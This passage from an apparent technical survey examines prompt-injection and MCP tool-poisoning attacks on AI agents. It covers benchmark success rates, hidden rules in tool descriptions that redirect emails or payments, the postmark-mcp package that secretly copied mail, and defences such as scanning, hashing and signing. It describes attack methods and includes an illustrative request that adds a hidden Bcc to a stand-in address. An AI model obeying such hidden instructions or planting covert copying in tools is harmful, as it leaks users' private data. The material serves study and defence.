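Invariant Labs published one successful run, which shows that the attack was possible but not how often it would work. Dziemian and colleagues report the largest public measurement, which comes from a competition. Gray Swan, a company that tests AI security, ran it with OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta, Amazon, the UK AI Security Institute and the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation. Excluding duplicates, 464 participants made 271,588 attempts against 13 models, and 8,648 attempts (about 3.2%) succeeded. The success rate was lowest against Claude Opus 4.5, at 0.5%, and highest against Gemini 2.5 Pro, at 8.5%. It was 4.82% against agents that called tools for tasks such as shopping or finance, 3.13% against agents that operated a computer through its screen, and 2.51% against coding agents.

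Some attackers forged passages that looked like the model's own reasoning or like messages from the user. Others invented official protocols that supposedly overrode the model's usual rules, or threatened it with penalties. One template, which presented the conversation as a simulation with a control panel, worked with small changes in 21 of the 41 scenarios and against nine models. Forged reasoning had the highest success rate, which fits the earlier finding that models do not reliably separate the roles in their input.

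Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound on vulnerability within a single turn, because participants could see the conversation and knew which action they had to cause. A real attacker would usually have to guess both. However, two counting rules lower the rates. In most scenarios, an attack counted only if the agent performed the harmful action and also hid it in its final answer, so a theft that the agent openly reported counted as a failed attack. The number of attempts also includes early drafts that participants never submitted for judging.

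A success rate per attempt also doesn't show how many scenarios are vulnerable. Participants found at least one successful attack on Claude Opus 4.5 in 13 of 37 scenarios, and on Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. Successes rose roughly in proportion to attempts throughout the competition, with no sign that participants were running out of ideas.

The competition now recurs, and the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), from the developer Reflection, lists further rounds up to August 2026. Newer models do much better on Gray Swan's benchmark. Attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 5 on 0.2% of single attempts and within 15 attempts in 2.0% of cases, according to its system card, the safety report that Anthropic published with the model in July. The 15-attempt rate was 16.5% for Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, according to the comparison quoted in Schneier (2026), *Anthropic’s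 Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*. In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 called Mythos 5.1 the company's most robust model so far on the external benchmark.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports a similar improvement on the company's own automated test, in which Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect injections, up from 96.23%. The share that succeeded therefore fell to 0.21% from 3.77%, the figure that TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gives for GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI used GPT-Red, its automated attacker, in both the training and the test, so the result may overstate how well Astra resists unfamiliar attacks.

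Results also vary with the kind of work. Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attack attempts in a restricted coding environment, according to VentureBeat's report on the model's February 2026 system card. When the same model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. With 200 attempts, the success rate rose to 78.6%, or 57.1% with extra safeguards. In July, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported no successful attack on Opus 5 across 129 browser test scenarios. If those scenarios were a random sample of what a browser agent meets, the true success rate could still be as high as about 2.3%, at 95% confidence.

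Small tests leave more room for error. *AutoRedClaw* reports attack success rates of 23.3% against OpenAI's coding agent Codex and 16.7% against Anthropic's Claude Code. With only 30 ordinary injection cases, that is a difference of two cases.

A more serious difficulty is that a test's result depends on the strength of the attacker as well as the model. By late 2025, frontier models resisted most attacks in fixed sets such as the AgentDojo benchmark. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) reports that recent Gemini models and some Claude models also fall to fewer than 1% of the human-devised attacks replayed from Gray Swan's competition. The researchers, who work at Google DeepMind, then built a stronger automated attacker that could learn from its failures. With weaker Gemini models powering it, the attacker failed against Gemini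 4 Argon in all 100 scenarios within 150 tries each. With Argon itself powering it, the attacker succeeded in 13 scenarios, and in 34 once it could use its full budget of up to 320 tries. Three open-weight models, Kimi K3, GLM-5.3 and DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, each resisted the attacker in only one scenario.

These figures do not measure how often an attacker could steal from a Gemini user, because Google had switched off the defences that normally surround the model and the attacker's goal was an irrelevant, usually harmless tool call. Training a model to refuse dangerous actions does little to stop it from logging a blood pressure reading. Kurakin and colleagues chose such goals to test whether the model obeys instructions in a tool result at all, and they argue that an attacker could combine harmless steps into a harmful sequence. Their results show that a model that older attacks almost never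 fool can still be fooled much more often by a better attacker.

### From one attempt to many

An attacker can usually try again. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*. At the 0.2% success rate reported for Claude Opus 5, that chance is about 18% for 100 attempts and about 86% for 1,000.

Attempts are rarely independent, because the failure of one is usually evidence of whether the next will succeed. If a model resists an instruction because it recognises the trick, it will probably resist a slightly reworded version too. Anthropic's published results show this effect. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports the figures for Opus 4.5, which come from a test that used especially strong attacks, so they are not comparable with those for the later models.

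| Model | Success on one attempt | Number of attempts | Reported success | Success if attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 33.6% | 38.2% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 63% | 99.2% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 5.5% | 7.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 2.0% | 3.0% |

The formula overstates the risk in every row, most of all for 100 attempts. One likely reason is that weaknesses are concentrated in particular tasks. Suppose that 98 of 100 tasks are immune and attacks on the other two succeed one time in ten. The average success rate per attempt is 0.2%, but 100 attempts on a randomly chosen task produce at least one success only about 2% of the time, because repeated attempts never succeed on the 98 immune tasks. An attacker who learns from each failure may do better than the formula predicts.

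Whether outcomes are independent matters much less when an attacker sends one message to many people. If the attack succeeds 0.2% of the time and the message reaches 10,000 assistants, the expected number of successes is 20, whether or not the outcomes are independent. If they are closely related, the message may fail almost everywhere or succeed against many assistants at once. *AgentCanary* (2026), another framework for testing agents, likewise finds that moderate success rates add up to a substantial risk as agents handle more interactions.

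All these calculations count only hostile messages, not the ordinary emails an assistant reads. TechRepublic notes that OpenAI's percentages are not the probability of a breach in real use. To estimate that probability, a company would also need to know how often attackers target its assistants and how closely their methods resemble those in the tests.

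## A test of twelve agent frameworks: instructions hidden in tool descriptions

In the GitHub attack, a legitimate tool fetched text written by a stranger. In tool poisoning, the attack is in the tool's description, so the user has to install the tool first, but the model then reads the attack whenever the host offers the tool, whatever the user asks for.

A poisoned tool can do harm without being called. Suppose the owner in the invoice example adds a free currency converter by an unknown author, and its description contains a rule that all new bills must use a certain bank account. When she asks the assistant to enter the invoice from Northgate Paper, the model reads that rule alongside the definition of `create_bill` and may put the attacker's account in `pay_to`. The converter won't appear in the record of calls because the model never called it.

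### The first demonstrations and measurements

Luca Beurer-Kellner and Marc Fischer named the attack in Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification*, published on 1 April 2025. They attacked Cursor, a coding agent, with a tool that added two numbers. The tool's description worked like that of the poisoned upload tool discussed earlier, and Cursor passed along the user's private login key and a file of credentials for other servers. Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but its dialog did not show the key.

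In their second experiment, the adding tool only had to be present. Its description contained a false technical rule that all emails must go to a particular address. When the user asked the agent to email someone else, it used a trusted server's email tool to send the message to the attacker. The change of recipient appeared in the agent's log only in the arguments of the call. *Poison everywhere* (Kosman, 2025) extended the warning from descriptions to every other part of a tool's schema.

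Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025), in *MCPTox*, measured how often such attacks work. They took 353 real tools from 45 public MCP servers and added one poisoned tool at a time to the list that the model read. They then gave the model a harmless request and recorded which call it wrote. An attack counted as successful only if the model used one of the honest tools to do the harm. Across 20 model settings, the average success rate was 36.5%, with a maximum of 72.8% for OpenAI's o1-mini. (The paper gives a total of 1,348 test cases, but its breakdown by type adds up to 1,497.)

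The most effective attacks tried to change one detail of the user's task, such as the recipient of an email, and succeeded 46.7% of the time. Attacks meant to make the model call a different tool succeeded 36.7% of the time if the user's request matched the poisoned tool's supposed purpose, and 26.7% if it did not. Claude 3.7 Sonnet refused most often, but in fewer than 3% of cases. Most attacks that failed did so because the model ignored the hidden instruction. In 18.9% of failures, the model called the poisoned tool itself, which could also be dangerous.

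An instruction that works in a tool result may not work in a tool description. When Wang and colleagues moved attacks from an older set of poisoned results into descriptions, the attacks succeeded 0.1% of the time against one model, compared with 41.8% for the team's own attacks. They suggest this is because a tool result is the newest text the model has read, while a description is one entry in a long list and has to specify when its instruction applies.

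*MCP-ITP* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) automated the version of the attack in which the poisoned tool is never called. One model wrote candidate descriptions and revised them after a second judged whether they looked malicious and a third tested whether they worked. On 548 cases from the earlier benchmark, automation raised the attack's success rate from 59.5% to 82.9% against o1-mini and from 44.8% to 78.4% against DeepSeek-V3. It made almost no difference against DeepSeek-R1, which had already followed 66.0% of the handwritten attacks.

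Li and colleagues' highest figure, 84.2% against GPT-3.5-turbo, should be read with some caution. They report that the handwritten attacks succeeded 48.2% of the time against this model, while Wang and colleagues had found rates between 1.2% and 6.8% for the same type of attack. The two groups must have run or scored something differently. Li and colleagues also ran each setting only once.

The rewritten descriptions were also harder to detect. One detector, AI-Infra-Guard using o1-mini, flagged 1.0% of them, compared with 17.2% of the handwritten ones. A stronger detector flagged 31.4% of the rewritten descriptions and 77.4% of the handwritten ones.

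### Twelve frameworks and a planted secret

Both groups examined the calls that models wrote. They did not test whether the calls went through and did any damage, or whether the surrounding software offered any protection. Most developers build their host applications with an agent framework, a code library that connects a model to its tools. The framework could in principle inspect a tool's description before passing it to the model.

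In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) tested the effect of instructions hidden in tool descriptions. They ran every combination of 12 set-ups, 18 models and 45 attack scenarios, 9,720 in total, from 22 to 24 July 2026. Eleven of the set-ups were frameworks, including LangChain, which had 126 million downloads a month. The twelfth, included for comparison, used OpenAI's API directly, without a framework.

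In each run, the agent connected to two MCP servers. The legitimate server had tools for reading and writing files and for sending data over the web, and the malicious one supplied the poisoned definitions. A shared folder contained a made-up secret. The researchers also ran a small web server that stood in for the attacker's and logged every request it received. They then gave the agent a harmless task, posing as its user.

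An attack counted as successful if either of two detectors found evidence of it. One searched the tool calls the agent had sent for the attacker's address, the secret or access to the planted file. The other checked whether the attacker's server received a request during the run. The researchers also reviewed 1,259 transcripts by hand. A second run of the whole test gave the same verdict in 93.5% of combinations.

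They skipped 268 combinations, and another 237 ended in errors. The attack succeeded in 2,113 of the remaining 9,215, which is 22.9%. The evidence for these successes varies in strength:

| What the detectors found | Runs | Share of successes | Share of all scored runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent sent a suspicious call to a tool, but nothing reached the attacker's server | 1,371 | 64.9% | 14.9% |
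| A request reached the attacker's server without the secret | 487 | 23.0% | 5.3% |
| The secret reached the attacker's server | 255 | 12.1% | 2.8% |

So the test verified a theft in only 2.8% of scored runs, but this is a minimum. In 1,067 of the 1,371 runs in the first row, the agent called a tool on the malicious MCP server, but the researchers' version of that tool only recorded the call and returned a dummy answer, so nothing could reach the attacker's server. A real attacker would have received whatever the call contained. In 290 other runs, the agent read the planted file, but nothing left the machine. The 22.9% is therefore best read as the rate at which agents carried out at least part of a hidden instruction.

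The overall rate also depends on the mix of models. Five of the 18 came from Anthropic and mostly resisted well. Without them, the rate would be 29.4%.

### Why two frameworks did better by accident

Attacks succeeded between 23.4% and 26.1% of the time against eight of the frameworks, and 25.3% of the time against the plain connection. On average, these eight frameworks protected users no better than having no framework. Shaikh and Montaruli also read the code and found that every framework passes tool descriptions to the model unchecked. They reported their findings to four organisations, all of which rejected the reports, for reasons that a later section covers.

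Some differences don't show up in the averages. With Meta's Llama 4 Maverick, the rates across these nine set-ups differed by as much as 36.5 percentage points, so a framework can have a large effect on a particular model even if nobody designed it to.

Two frameworks had clearly lower attack success rates. One was Pydantic AI, at 16.6%, which does not allow two tools with the same name. In 14 of the scenarios, the malicious server copied the name of a legitimate tool, so loading failed and the researchers recorded 250 runs as resistant before a model had read anything. Without those runs, the attack succeeded in 123 of 492, or 25.0%, similar to the rates for the other frameworks.

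Even this advantage is partly due to how the test was set up. For LangChain and four other frameworks, the researchers wrote code that merged the two lists of tools and kept the malicious version when two tools had the same name, because the usual connectors would have failed or dropped one of the definitions. Without this code, some of those frameworks might also have blocked the same scenarios by accident.

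AG2 had the lowest rate, 4.6%, and none of its requests reached the attacker's server. The models still wrote the malicious calls, but the part of AG2 that executes calls rarely completed the ones that send data out. Shaikh and Montaruli warn against choosing AG2 for security because of this result. They did not measure how well the agents worked without an attack, so AG2 may also have failed to send data when a user wanted it to.

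The framework smolagents did worst, at 34.4%. Its agents call tools by writing Python code, and the model sees each tool as Python code with a comment rather than as a structured definition. The researchers think that safety training on structured definitions carries over poorly to this form, which is plausible, but they did not test it separately.

### Are more capable models easier to fool?

Attack success depended far more on the model than on the framework. Attacks succeeded in 0.4% of scored runs with Claude Fable 5 and in 49.7% with Amazon's Nova Pro. The figure for Fable 5 leaves out runs that the provider's content filter stopped before the model wrote anything. A blocked run leaks nothing, but counting these runs as successful attacks would raise the figure to 13.5%.

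Wang and colleagues had concluded that more capable models are often more susceptible, because the attack exploits their skill at following instructions. *Weighing the Envelope*, a November 2026 paper on defences for agents, repeats this claim, but the original data only partly support it. The attack succeeded more often on Alibaba's Qwen3 models when their reasoning mode was switched on, by 22 to 35 percentage points depending on model size. But the success rate did not consistently rise or fall with size. With reasoning on, it was 41.8% for the smallest model, 27.1% for the next, 58.5% for the third and 50.6% for the largest.

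The newer results divide by developer:

| Developer | Weaker or older model | Stronger or newer model | Fits the claim? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Claude Sonnet 4.5: 14.5% | Claude Sonnet 5: 1.9% | No |
| OpenAI | GPT-OSS-120B: 38.1% | GPT-5.5: 12.4% | No |
| Mistral (size) | Ministral 3 14B: 34.3% | Mistral Large 3: 43.7% | Yes |
| Mistral (generation) | Mistral Large 2: 21.6% | Mistral Large 3: 43.7% | Yes |
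| Meta | Llama 4 Scout: 28.1% | Llama 4 Maverick: 44.1% | Yes |

A likely explanation is that greater capability makes models more vulnerable, while safety training makes them less so. A weak model may miss the hidden instruction or fail to carry it out, and a stronger one can carry it out unless its developer has trained it not to. The refusals also support this explanation. None of the models that Wang and colleagues tested in 2025 refused as often as 3% of the time, whereas Claude Opus 4.8 explicitly refused, citing the poisoned description, in 223 of its 530 scored runs. Eight attacks succeeded against it. Shaikh and Montaruli attribute most of the variation to each company's investment in alignment, meaning training that makes a model behave as intended. But they also suggest that better instruction-following may make models more vulnerable, which is hard to reconcile with their own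 results for Anthropic.

In four of its ten failures, Claude Sonnet 5 identified the text as a prompt injection and then made the tool call anyway.

A low score may also reflect a failure to call tools rather than resistance to the attacks. DeepSeek-R1 followed 70.9% of the attacks in the 2025 benchmark but only 3.6% in the new study. The attacks and scoring differed, but the model may also have seldom managed to call any tool in the new set-up. DeepSeek-R1 and Google's Gemma 3 each had the same attack success rate in all nine of the similar set-ups, which would be odd if they had been assessing each attack separately. The study did not include tests of the same tasks without poisoned descriptions, which would have settled the matter.

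The scenarios were also variations on published attacks. Models trained after 2025 may have seen similar examples, so part of Anthropic's lead could come from familiarity. Every model faced the same scenarios, and an attacker who adjusted the wording to each model, as Li and colleagues did, would probably do better. The improvement could be large, since stronger attackers did much better than older ones in the tests of injected tool results.

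Success depended heavily on wording, even within the fixed set. Instructions written in Chinese or German and presented as compliance rules succeeded 66.0% of the time, while those hidden in invisible characters failed in all 209 scored runs. Each task was a single request, so the study provides little evidence of what a poisoned description does over a long session, where it can influence many more calls.

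### Scanning descriptions

If the frameworks and some of the models don't stop these attacks, software could inspect the descriptions first. Ten days after its disclosure, Invariant Labs released a scanner for this purpose, announced in *Introducing MCP-Scan* (2025). Shaikh and Montaruli built a simple scanner to see how well basic checks would work. It looks for encoded text, descriptions longer than 500 characters, and commands followed by a tool's name or a web address.

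The scanner caught 20 of the 45 scenarios and wrongly flagged nine of 125 harmless descriptions (7.2%) from ten public servers. Without the other two checks, the search for commands would have caught the same 20 scenarios and flagged only six harmless descriptions. The 500-character limit on descriptions also fits poorly with Anthropic's advice to developers, since three or four good sentences can easily exceed it.

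Six of the nine false alarms came from descriptions that mention another tool for a good reason, such as "Use read_text_file instead". Any scanner of this kind faces this problem, because legitimate descriptions also contain many instructions. The 25 scenarios the scanner missed either placed the attack outside the description or worded it in a way the patterns did not cover, for instance as a company policy or in another language.

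False alarms become a bigger problem when poisoned tools are rare. Suppose one in 100 descriptions in a public directory is poisoned and the scanner performs as it did in the test. Among 10,000 descriptions, it would catch about 44 of the 100 poisoned ones and flag about 713 harmless ones. Only about 6% of its warnings would be correct, so people who have to review them all may soon stop reading carefully.

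Shaikh and Montaruli therefore recommend using scanning only alongside other measures, including checking tool results and storing a fingerprint of each description to detect later changes.

### Writing the description from the code

TRUSTDESC, a system by Ye and colleagues, discards every tool description and writes a new one from the tool's source code, so it doesn't have to judge which descriptions look suspicious. The currency converter's rule about bank accounts should not appear in the new description, because the program only converts currency. The method works equally well for descriptions that praise the tool.

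The system first finds the function that starts the tool and follows its calls to collect the code that the tool can reach. A language model then removes branches that never run, because they could lead to false claims. In one case, a charting function had chart-style options that the tool never used, and even a strong model wrongly described them as available until the system removed them.

A language model then writes the description from what is left. Because an attacker could also plant misleading words in the code, the system deletes all comments, shortens names to 20 characters and removes promotional words from them.

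Finally, the system turns the claims in the draft into small tasks and has an agent carry them out. A draft for a spreadsheet tool, for example, included the claim that the tool adds a missing equals sign to a formula. When the agent tried it, the tool returned an error, so the system corrected the description.

Ye and colleagues tested the generated descriptions on 52 tools from 12 MCP servers. An agent completed 84.1% of 208 tasks with the original descriptions and 87.7% with the new ones, averaged over the four models that wrote them. The test may slightly overstate the gain, because the researchers derived half of the tasks from the generated descriptions. Still, it gives no sign that the security makes the tools less useful. Many of the original descriptions were poor, and seven of the 52 tools had no description of their inputs. With the cheapest commercial model, a new description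 took about 26 seconds to generate and cost 1.3 cents.

The evidence on security is thinner. The researchers ran the system on seven publicly known poisoned tools and read the new descriptions, which contained none of the harmful or misleading phrases. They did not repeat the attacks. They also had a model rename parts of a tool's code over 15 rounds to make the tool look more attractive than an otherwise identical one. Agents chose the altered tool between 44.7% and 67.4% of the time, where 50% would mean no effect, and the renaming did not become more effective from round to round.

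The method needs the source code, which rules out most tools that run on someone else's servers. Ye and colleagues had to drop eight of the 20 servers they first selected because these were remote or required paid accounts. The owner in the invoice example could use the method on a converter she installs on her own machine, but not on the accounting service. The method also assumes that the code is not malicious. If the converter's program copied her files to a stranger, removing the hidden instructions from its description would not stop the copying.

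## The postmark-mcp package: a supplier that changed its tool after release

In September 2025 the security company Koi reported what it called the first malicious MCP server found in real use. The package, postmark-mcp, let an assistant send email through Postmark, a service that delivers mail for other companies' software. An update added code that sent a hidden copy of every message to an address that apparently belonged to the package's author.

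### One added line

The package was on npm, a public registry from which programmers download JavaScript code. Postmark had an official MCP server of the same name on GitHub but had not published it on npm, so the name was available there. A developer with no connection to the company copied the official code and uploaded it. The developer's public profile would have reassured anyone who checked. Koi found a real name and legitimate projects, and The Hacker News (2025) counted 31 other packages by the same developer.

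According to Koi, versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 worked normally. Version 1.0.16 added one line that put an extra address in the BCC field, which recipients of an email can't see. Koi's monitoring software flagged the change in behaviour, and its researchers then found the line. The developer didn't reply when they asked for an explanation, but did delete the package from npm. Deleting it did not remove the copies people had already installed, which went on copying mail to the extra address.

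Postmark said it had no involvement with the package and that its own service remained secure. It told users to remove the package, check their email logs and consider replacing any passwords or keys they had sent by email.

Two public databases also record 1.0.16 as the first malicious version. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025) credits Google's open-source security team but doesn't describe an analysis. Snyk's *Malicious Package Affecting postmark-mcp package* (2025) says the package was "reportedly" modified and credits Koi's researcher, so it isn't independent confirmation.

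The number of victims is much less certain than the version number:

| Figure | Basis |
|---|---|
| 1,643 downloads in total | Reported by The Hacker News |
| 1,500 downloads a week | Reported by Koi |
| About 300 organisations | Koi's guess that 20% of a week's downloads were in active use, each at a different organisation |
| 3,000 to 15,000 copied emails a day | Koi's guess that each organisation sent 10 to 50 emails a day |

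Koi calls the last two figures a "guestimate". It did not publish how many messages reached the address. Some downloads were of versions without the added line, and automated systems may have made others.

Koi also writes that a tool can be legitimate "for months" before it becomes malicious, but The Hacker News dates the first upload to 15 September and version 1.0.16 to 17 September. If those dates are right, users had only two days to come to trust the harmless versions, and the weekly figure would cover nearly the whole life of the package. Both databases published their entries on 26 September, nine days after the malicious release.

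### Why a resistant model makes no difference

Suppose the owner in the invoice example uses such a package to tell Northgate Paper that she has paid. The model writes a correct call (the data and both formats are simplified and fictitious):

```json
{"name": "send_email",
 "input": {"to": "billing@northgate.example",
           "subject": "Invoice 2207",
           "body": "We have paid EUR 480 today."}}
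```

The package then builds its own request to the mail service:

```json
{"To": "billing@northgate.example",
 "Bcc": "author@copies.example",
 "Subject": "Invoice 2207",
 "TextBody": "We have paid EUR 480 today."}
```

The model is never shown the second request. It receives a result that correctly confirms the email was sent. Because the attack uses no hidden instruction, even a model that resisted every prompt injection would make the same call. If the host requires the owner to confirm the call, the dialog shows the model's arguments, which are also correct.

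Meta's Rule of Two would not flag this assistant either. If it reads only the owner's words, it has access to private data and can communicate externally, but it processes no untrustworthy input. The danger here is in the code that carries out the call, and the rule covers only what the model reads. A network filter that allowed connections only to the mail service would also let the copy through, since it leaves as ordinary mail. The owner could find the copy in the service's email logs, where Koi recommends looking.

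### What an honest supplier receives

The arguments of each call already contain some private information, so a supplier can receive it without a hidden line of code. A mail tool needs the recipient and the full text of the message. The accounting service learns whom the firm pays, how much and into which account. Once a remote supplier has this data, the host can't control how long the supplier stores it or who reads it.

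The model may also send more information than the task requires. If the owner has been discussing a dispute with Northgate Paper and asks for the legal deadline for a claim, the model might include the supplier's name and the disputed sum in a web search. The search company would then learn about the dispute, even though it hadn't requested those details.

Trail of Bits' *How MCP servers can steal your conversation history* (2025) describes an extreme, malicious case in which a poisoned tool description directs the model to forward the whole conversation to the tool's operator when the user types a common phrase such as "thank you". Even without such an instruction, a loosely worded schema field in an honest supplier's tool, like `recent_correspondence` in the earlier example, could lead the model to send some of the same text.

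*Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), security guidance from the US National Security Agency, recommends a local MCP server for private data, along with filters on outgoing traffic. A local server can keep a search of a user's files on the user's own machine, but it can't contain the data when a tool's purpose is to send it elsewhere, as with postmark-mcp, which users installed locally.

### Changes after approval

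Security researchers call it a rug pull when a supplier gains approval for a harmless tool and then changes it. How easily the supplier can do this depends on where the tool runs.

With a local tool, the user has a copy of the code. The host's configuration contains the command that starts the server, and this command can specify an exact version. A user who had fixed postmark-mcp at 1.0.15 would have kept that version when 1.0.16 came out. If the command specifies the latest version instead, the package manager may install new code without anyone deciding to accept it.

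The user of a remote tool has only its address. The operator can change the code behind that address between calls, or send different answers to different customers. *MCPThreatHive* (2026) notes that MCP does not require suppliers to sign their tool definitions or fix their versions, so a server may behave differently after an audit. The operator may also change without the user's knowledge. In one scenario from *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, a trusted server's domain registration expires, an attacker buys the domain, and every client connects to the attacker's server.

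The NSA's example of a change after approval is Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited*, a demonstration from April 2025. The researchers connected an agent to a trusted MCP server for reading and sending WhatsApp messages, and to their own MCP server, which had a tool that supplied a random fact of the day. When the user first installed and approved the fact tool, its description was harmless.

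The second time the server started, it supplied a new description with a false rule that all WhatsApp messages had to go through a "proxy" number, along with the user's recent messages. The host did not point out the change. When the user next asked the agent to send a message, the model called the trusted WhatsApp tool with the attacker's number and the stolen messages. As in the earlier email experiment, the attack did not require the model to call the malicious tool.

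Cursor, the host in the demonstration, asked the user for confirmation, so the NSA's statement that the messages leaked "without user notice or approval" is slightly too strong. But the dialog showed an unfamiliar phone number and the word "Hi", followed by so many spaces that the user had to scroll right to see the stolen text. A user could have approved the call without understanding it.

This attack depended on the model following the new description, so a more resistant model might have stopped it. Invariant Labs points out that sandboxing the malicious server would not have stopped the attack, because the trusted server sent the data.

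### Name collisions

Postmark-mcp also benefited from having the same name as the official project on another site. *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Hou, Zhao and colleagues, 2025) describes similar confusion between servers. An attacker could register `mcp-github` to imitate `github-mcp`, and no central authority controls the names. A user who chooses the wrong server may give it a real access token.

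Tool names can also clash. If the owner has a legitimate `send_email` tool and adds a server with another tool of the same name, the host may send her message to the wrong one. The NSA warns that clients often cannot specify a unique tool, and that some hosts look up names in public registries or local folders and can load an attacker's code by mistake.

The server prefixes that MCP recommends prevent accidental mix-ups between two connected tools, but they don't help someone who has installed only the impostor, because no other connected tool has a conflicting name.

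### What each safeguard misses

The two attacks changed different things. The update to postmark-mcp changed the code and, by Koi's account, nothing else. The WhatsApp attack changed the description, and the program that did so could stay the same, since it was written to switch on its second launch. A safeguard can therefore stop one and miss the other:

| Safeguard | Hidden copies in postmark-mcp | New description in the WhatsApp attack |
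|---|---|---|
| Fixed version | Works if the user fixed an earlier version | Fails, because the same version supplies both descriptions |
| Stored hash of the definition | Fails if the definition stays the same | Detects the change |
| Signed definition | Fails if the author signs it | Detects the change, but the attacker can sign the new text and ask for approval |
| Review before listing | Fails if the reviewer saw only an earlier version | Works if the reviewer reads the code and finds the switch |

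Staying on one version of a package protects users only if that version is safe. Someone who first installed postmark-mcp on 18 September and stayed on the version then current would have kept the malicious line. Old versions can also contain flaws that later ones repair. OSV's *CVE-2026-46555* (2026) describes a WhatsApp MCP server that, before version 0.2.1, accepted commands on the user's machine without authentication, which let an attacker send messages and extract files. Users of those versions need the update, so they have to decide again whether to trust new code.

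A hash is a short value computed from a text, and in practice any edit to the text changes it. *MCP-38* recommends that clients store the hash of each approved definition and ask the user again if it changes. This check is simple and doesn't depend on recognising suspicious language. But honest suppliers also correct their descriptions, and a user who gets many alerts about harmless changes may approve a dangerous one out of habit.

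*ETDI* (Bhatt, Narajala and Habler, 2025) proposes adding signatures and version numbers to the hash. The supplier signs each definition, including its description, schema and permissions, with a private key. The client uses the matching public key to check that nobody else has altered the definition, then compares it with the version the user approved. If the version number is the same but the hash differs, the client reports tampering and asks for approval again. A new version also needs approval.

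A signature proves who signed a definition, but not that the tool is safe. The author of postmark-mcp could have signed every version with a valid key. A client could have detected the impersonation only by requiring packages of that name to be signed with Postmark's own key.

Bhatt and colleagues also let the supplier include a hash of the tool's interface, which specifies what requests and replies look like. They say this would reveal changes behind an unchanged description. The hash would reveal a new input field but not an extra BCC recipient, which changes neither the model's request nor the reply. It would also miss their own example of a rug pull, a wallpaper tool that starts uploading financial documents without changing its version number. They published sample code but no measurements of how many attacks the system stops. Both suppliers and clients would need to support the system.

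A supplier's genuine account can distribute malicious code. In November 2025, OSV (2025) listed three versions of `@postman/postman-mcp-server` as malicious. The package is under the name of Postman, a different software company from Postmark. The entry links to reports on a wider campaign that compromised prominent npm packages. A user who chose the official name could still have installed one of these versions.

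### Registries and tests of behaviour

Registries could check tools before listing them, but many public ones check little. Li and Gao (2025) collected 67,057 servers from six registries for *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*. Four of the registries linked to code stored elsewhere, usually without checking later that the same person still controlled it. If a developer deletes or renames a GitHub account, an attacker may be able to claim the old name, so that the registry's link leads to the attacker's account. On one registry, some configuration examples exposed the owners' access tokens, which an attacker could use to alter the servers directly.

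Li and Gao also scanned servers from those four indexes and found 833 with exploitable flaws in their code and 18 with suspicious descriptions. These figures do not measure how many suppliers are malicious, because most flawed code is probably accidental and a scan of descriptions would have missed postmark-mcp.

An automatic review may also give a buyer little to act on. The skills.sh marketplace page *whatsapp-mcp* (2026) shows an audit of a skill, a package that extends what an agent can do. The audit, dated 4 April 2026, rates the skill medium risk because it reads messages written by other people. That is a fair warning about prompt injection, but it would apply to any tool that reads WhatsApp messages, and the audit doesn't cover later versions of the skill.

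Running a tool and watching what it does gives better evidence. Ravindran and Deochake (2026), in *ToolGuardian*, built malicious versions of eight real tools and left their descriptions unchanged. They then gave a set of fixed rules increasing amounts of evidence about all 16 tools:

| Evidence available to the rules | Malicious tools rejected | Harmless tools rejected |
|---|---|---|
| Descriptions | 5 of 8 | 5 of 8 |
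| Also the tool's requests to the operating system | 5 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| Also its observed effects in a test environment | 6 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| Also its source code | 7 of 8 | 2 of 8 |

With descriptions alone, the rules rejected as many harmless tools as malicious ones. They were most accurate overall, at 88%, when they used observed effects, but they still restricted all eight harmless tools. Reading the source code exposed one more malicious tool, but it also led the rules to reject two harmless ones with powerful functions.

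Sixteen tools are too few for a reliable error rate, but the method suits a case like postmark-mcp. A test that sends an email to a simulated mail service and records every recipient would reveal the extra address. The supplier could evade it by adding the address only after a certain date or for certain customers. The customer also has to repeat the test for every release, and may not know when a remote tool has a new one.

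## Scans of public tool servers: missing authentication and excessive permissions

The developer of postmark-mcp deliberately copied other people's email. An honest supplier can also put its customers at risk if its server accepts requests from anyone or has more permissions on their accounts than its tools need. Two studies from 2026 looked for these faults in servers on the public internet. Their main figures, 40.55% without authentication and 91.8% without OAuth, are easy to confuse.

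Authentication establishes who is calling, and authorization determines what that caller may do. When the accounting service receives a `create_bill` request, it must check that the program acts for the firm's owner and that it may record bills. The service uses the owner's access token for both checks, and the token's scopes, such as `bills:read` or `bills:write`, specify which actions are allowed. Anyone who steals a copy of the token can make the same requests.

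Some servers use a static key, a long password that the customer copies into the host's settings. The key works until someone revokes it, with no login or consent page. OAuth instead gives each program its own token.

### How a user connects an account

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) specifies the process for remote servers. An authorization server, which may belong to the tool's supplier or to another company, logs the user in and issues the tokens. The owner in the invoice example would connect her assistant to the accounting service like this:

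1. The assistant's client sends a request without a token. The accounting service refuses it and tells the client where to find its authorization server.
2. The client identifies itself to the authorization server and gives a redirect address, where it will wait for the answer.
3. The client invents a one-time secret and opens the owner's browser at the authorization server. The request includes a value computed from the secret, the scopes the client wants and the server it wants to use.
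4. The owner logs in, reads a consent page and approves.
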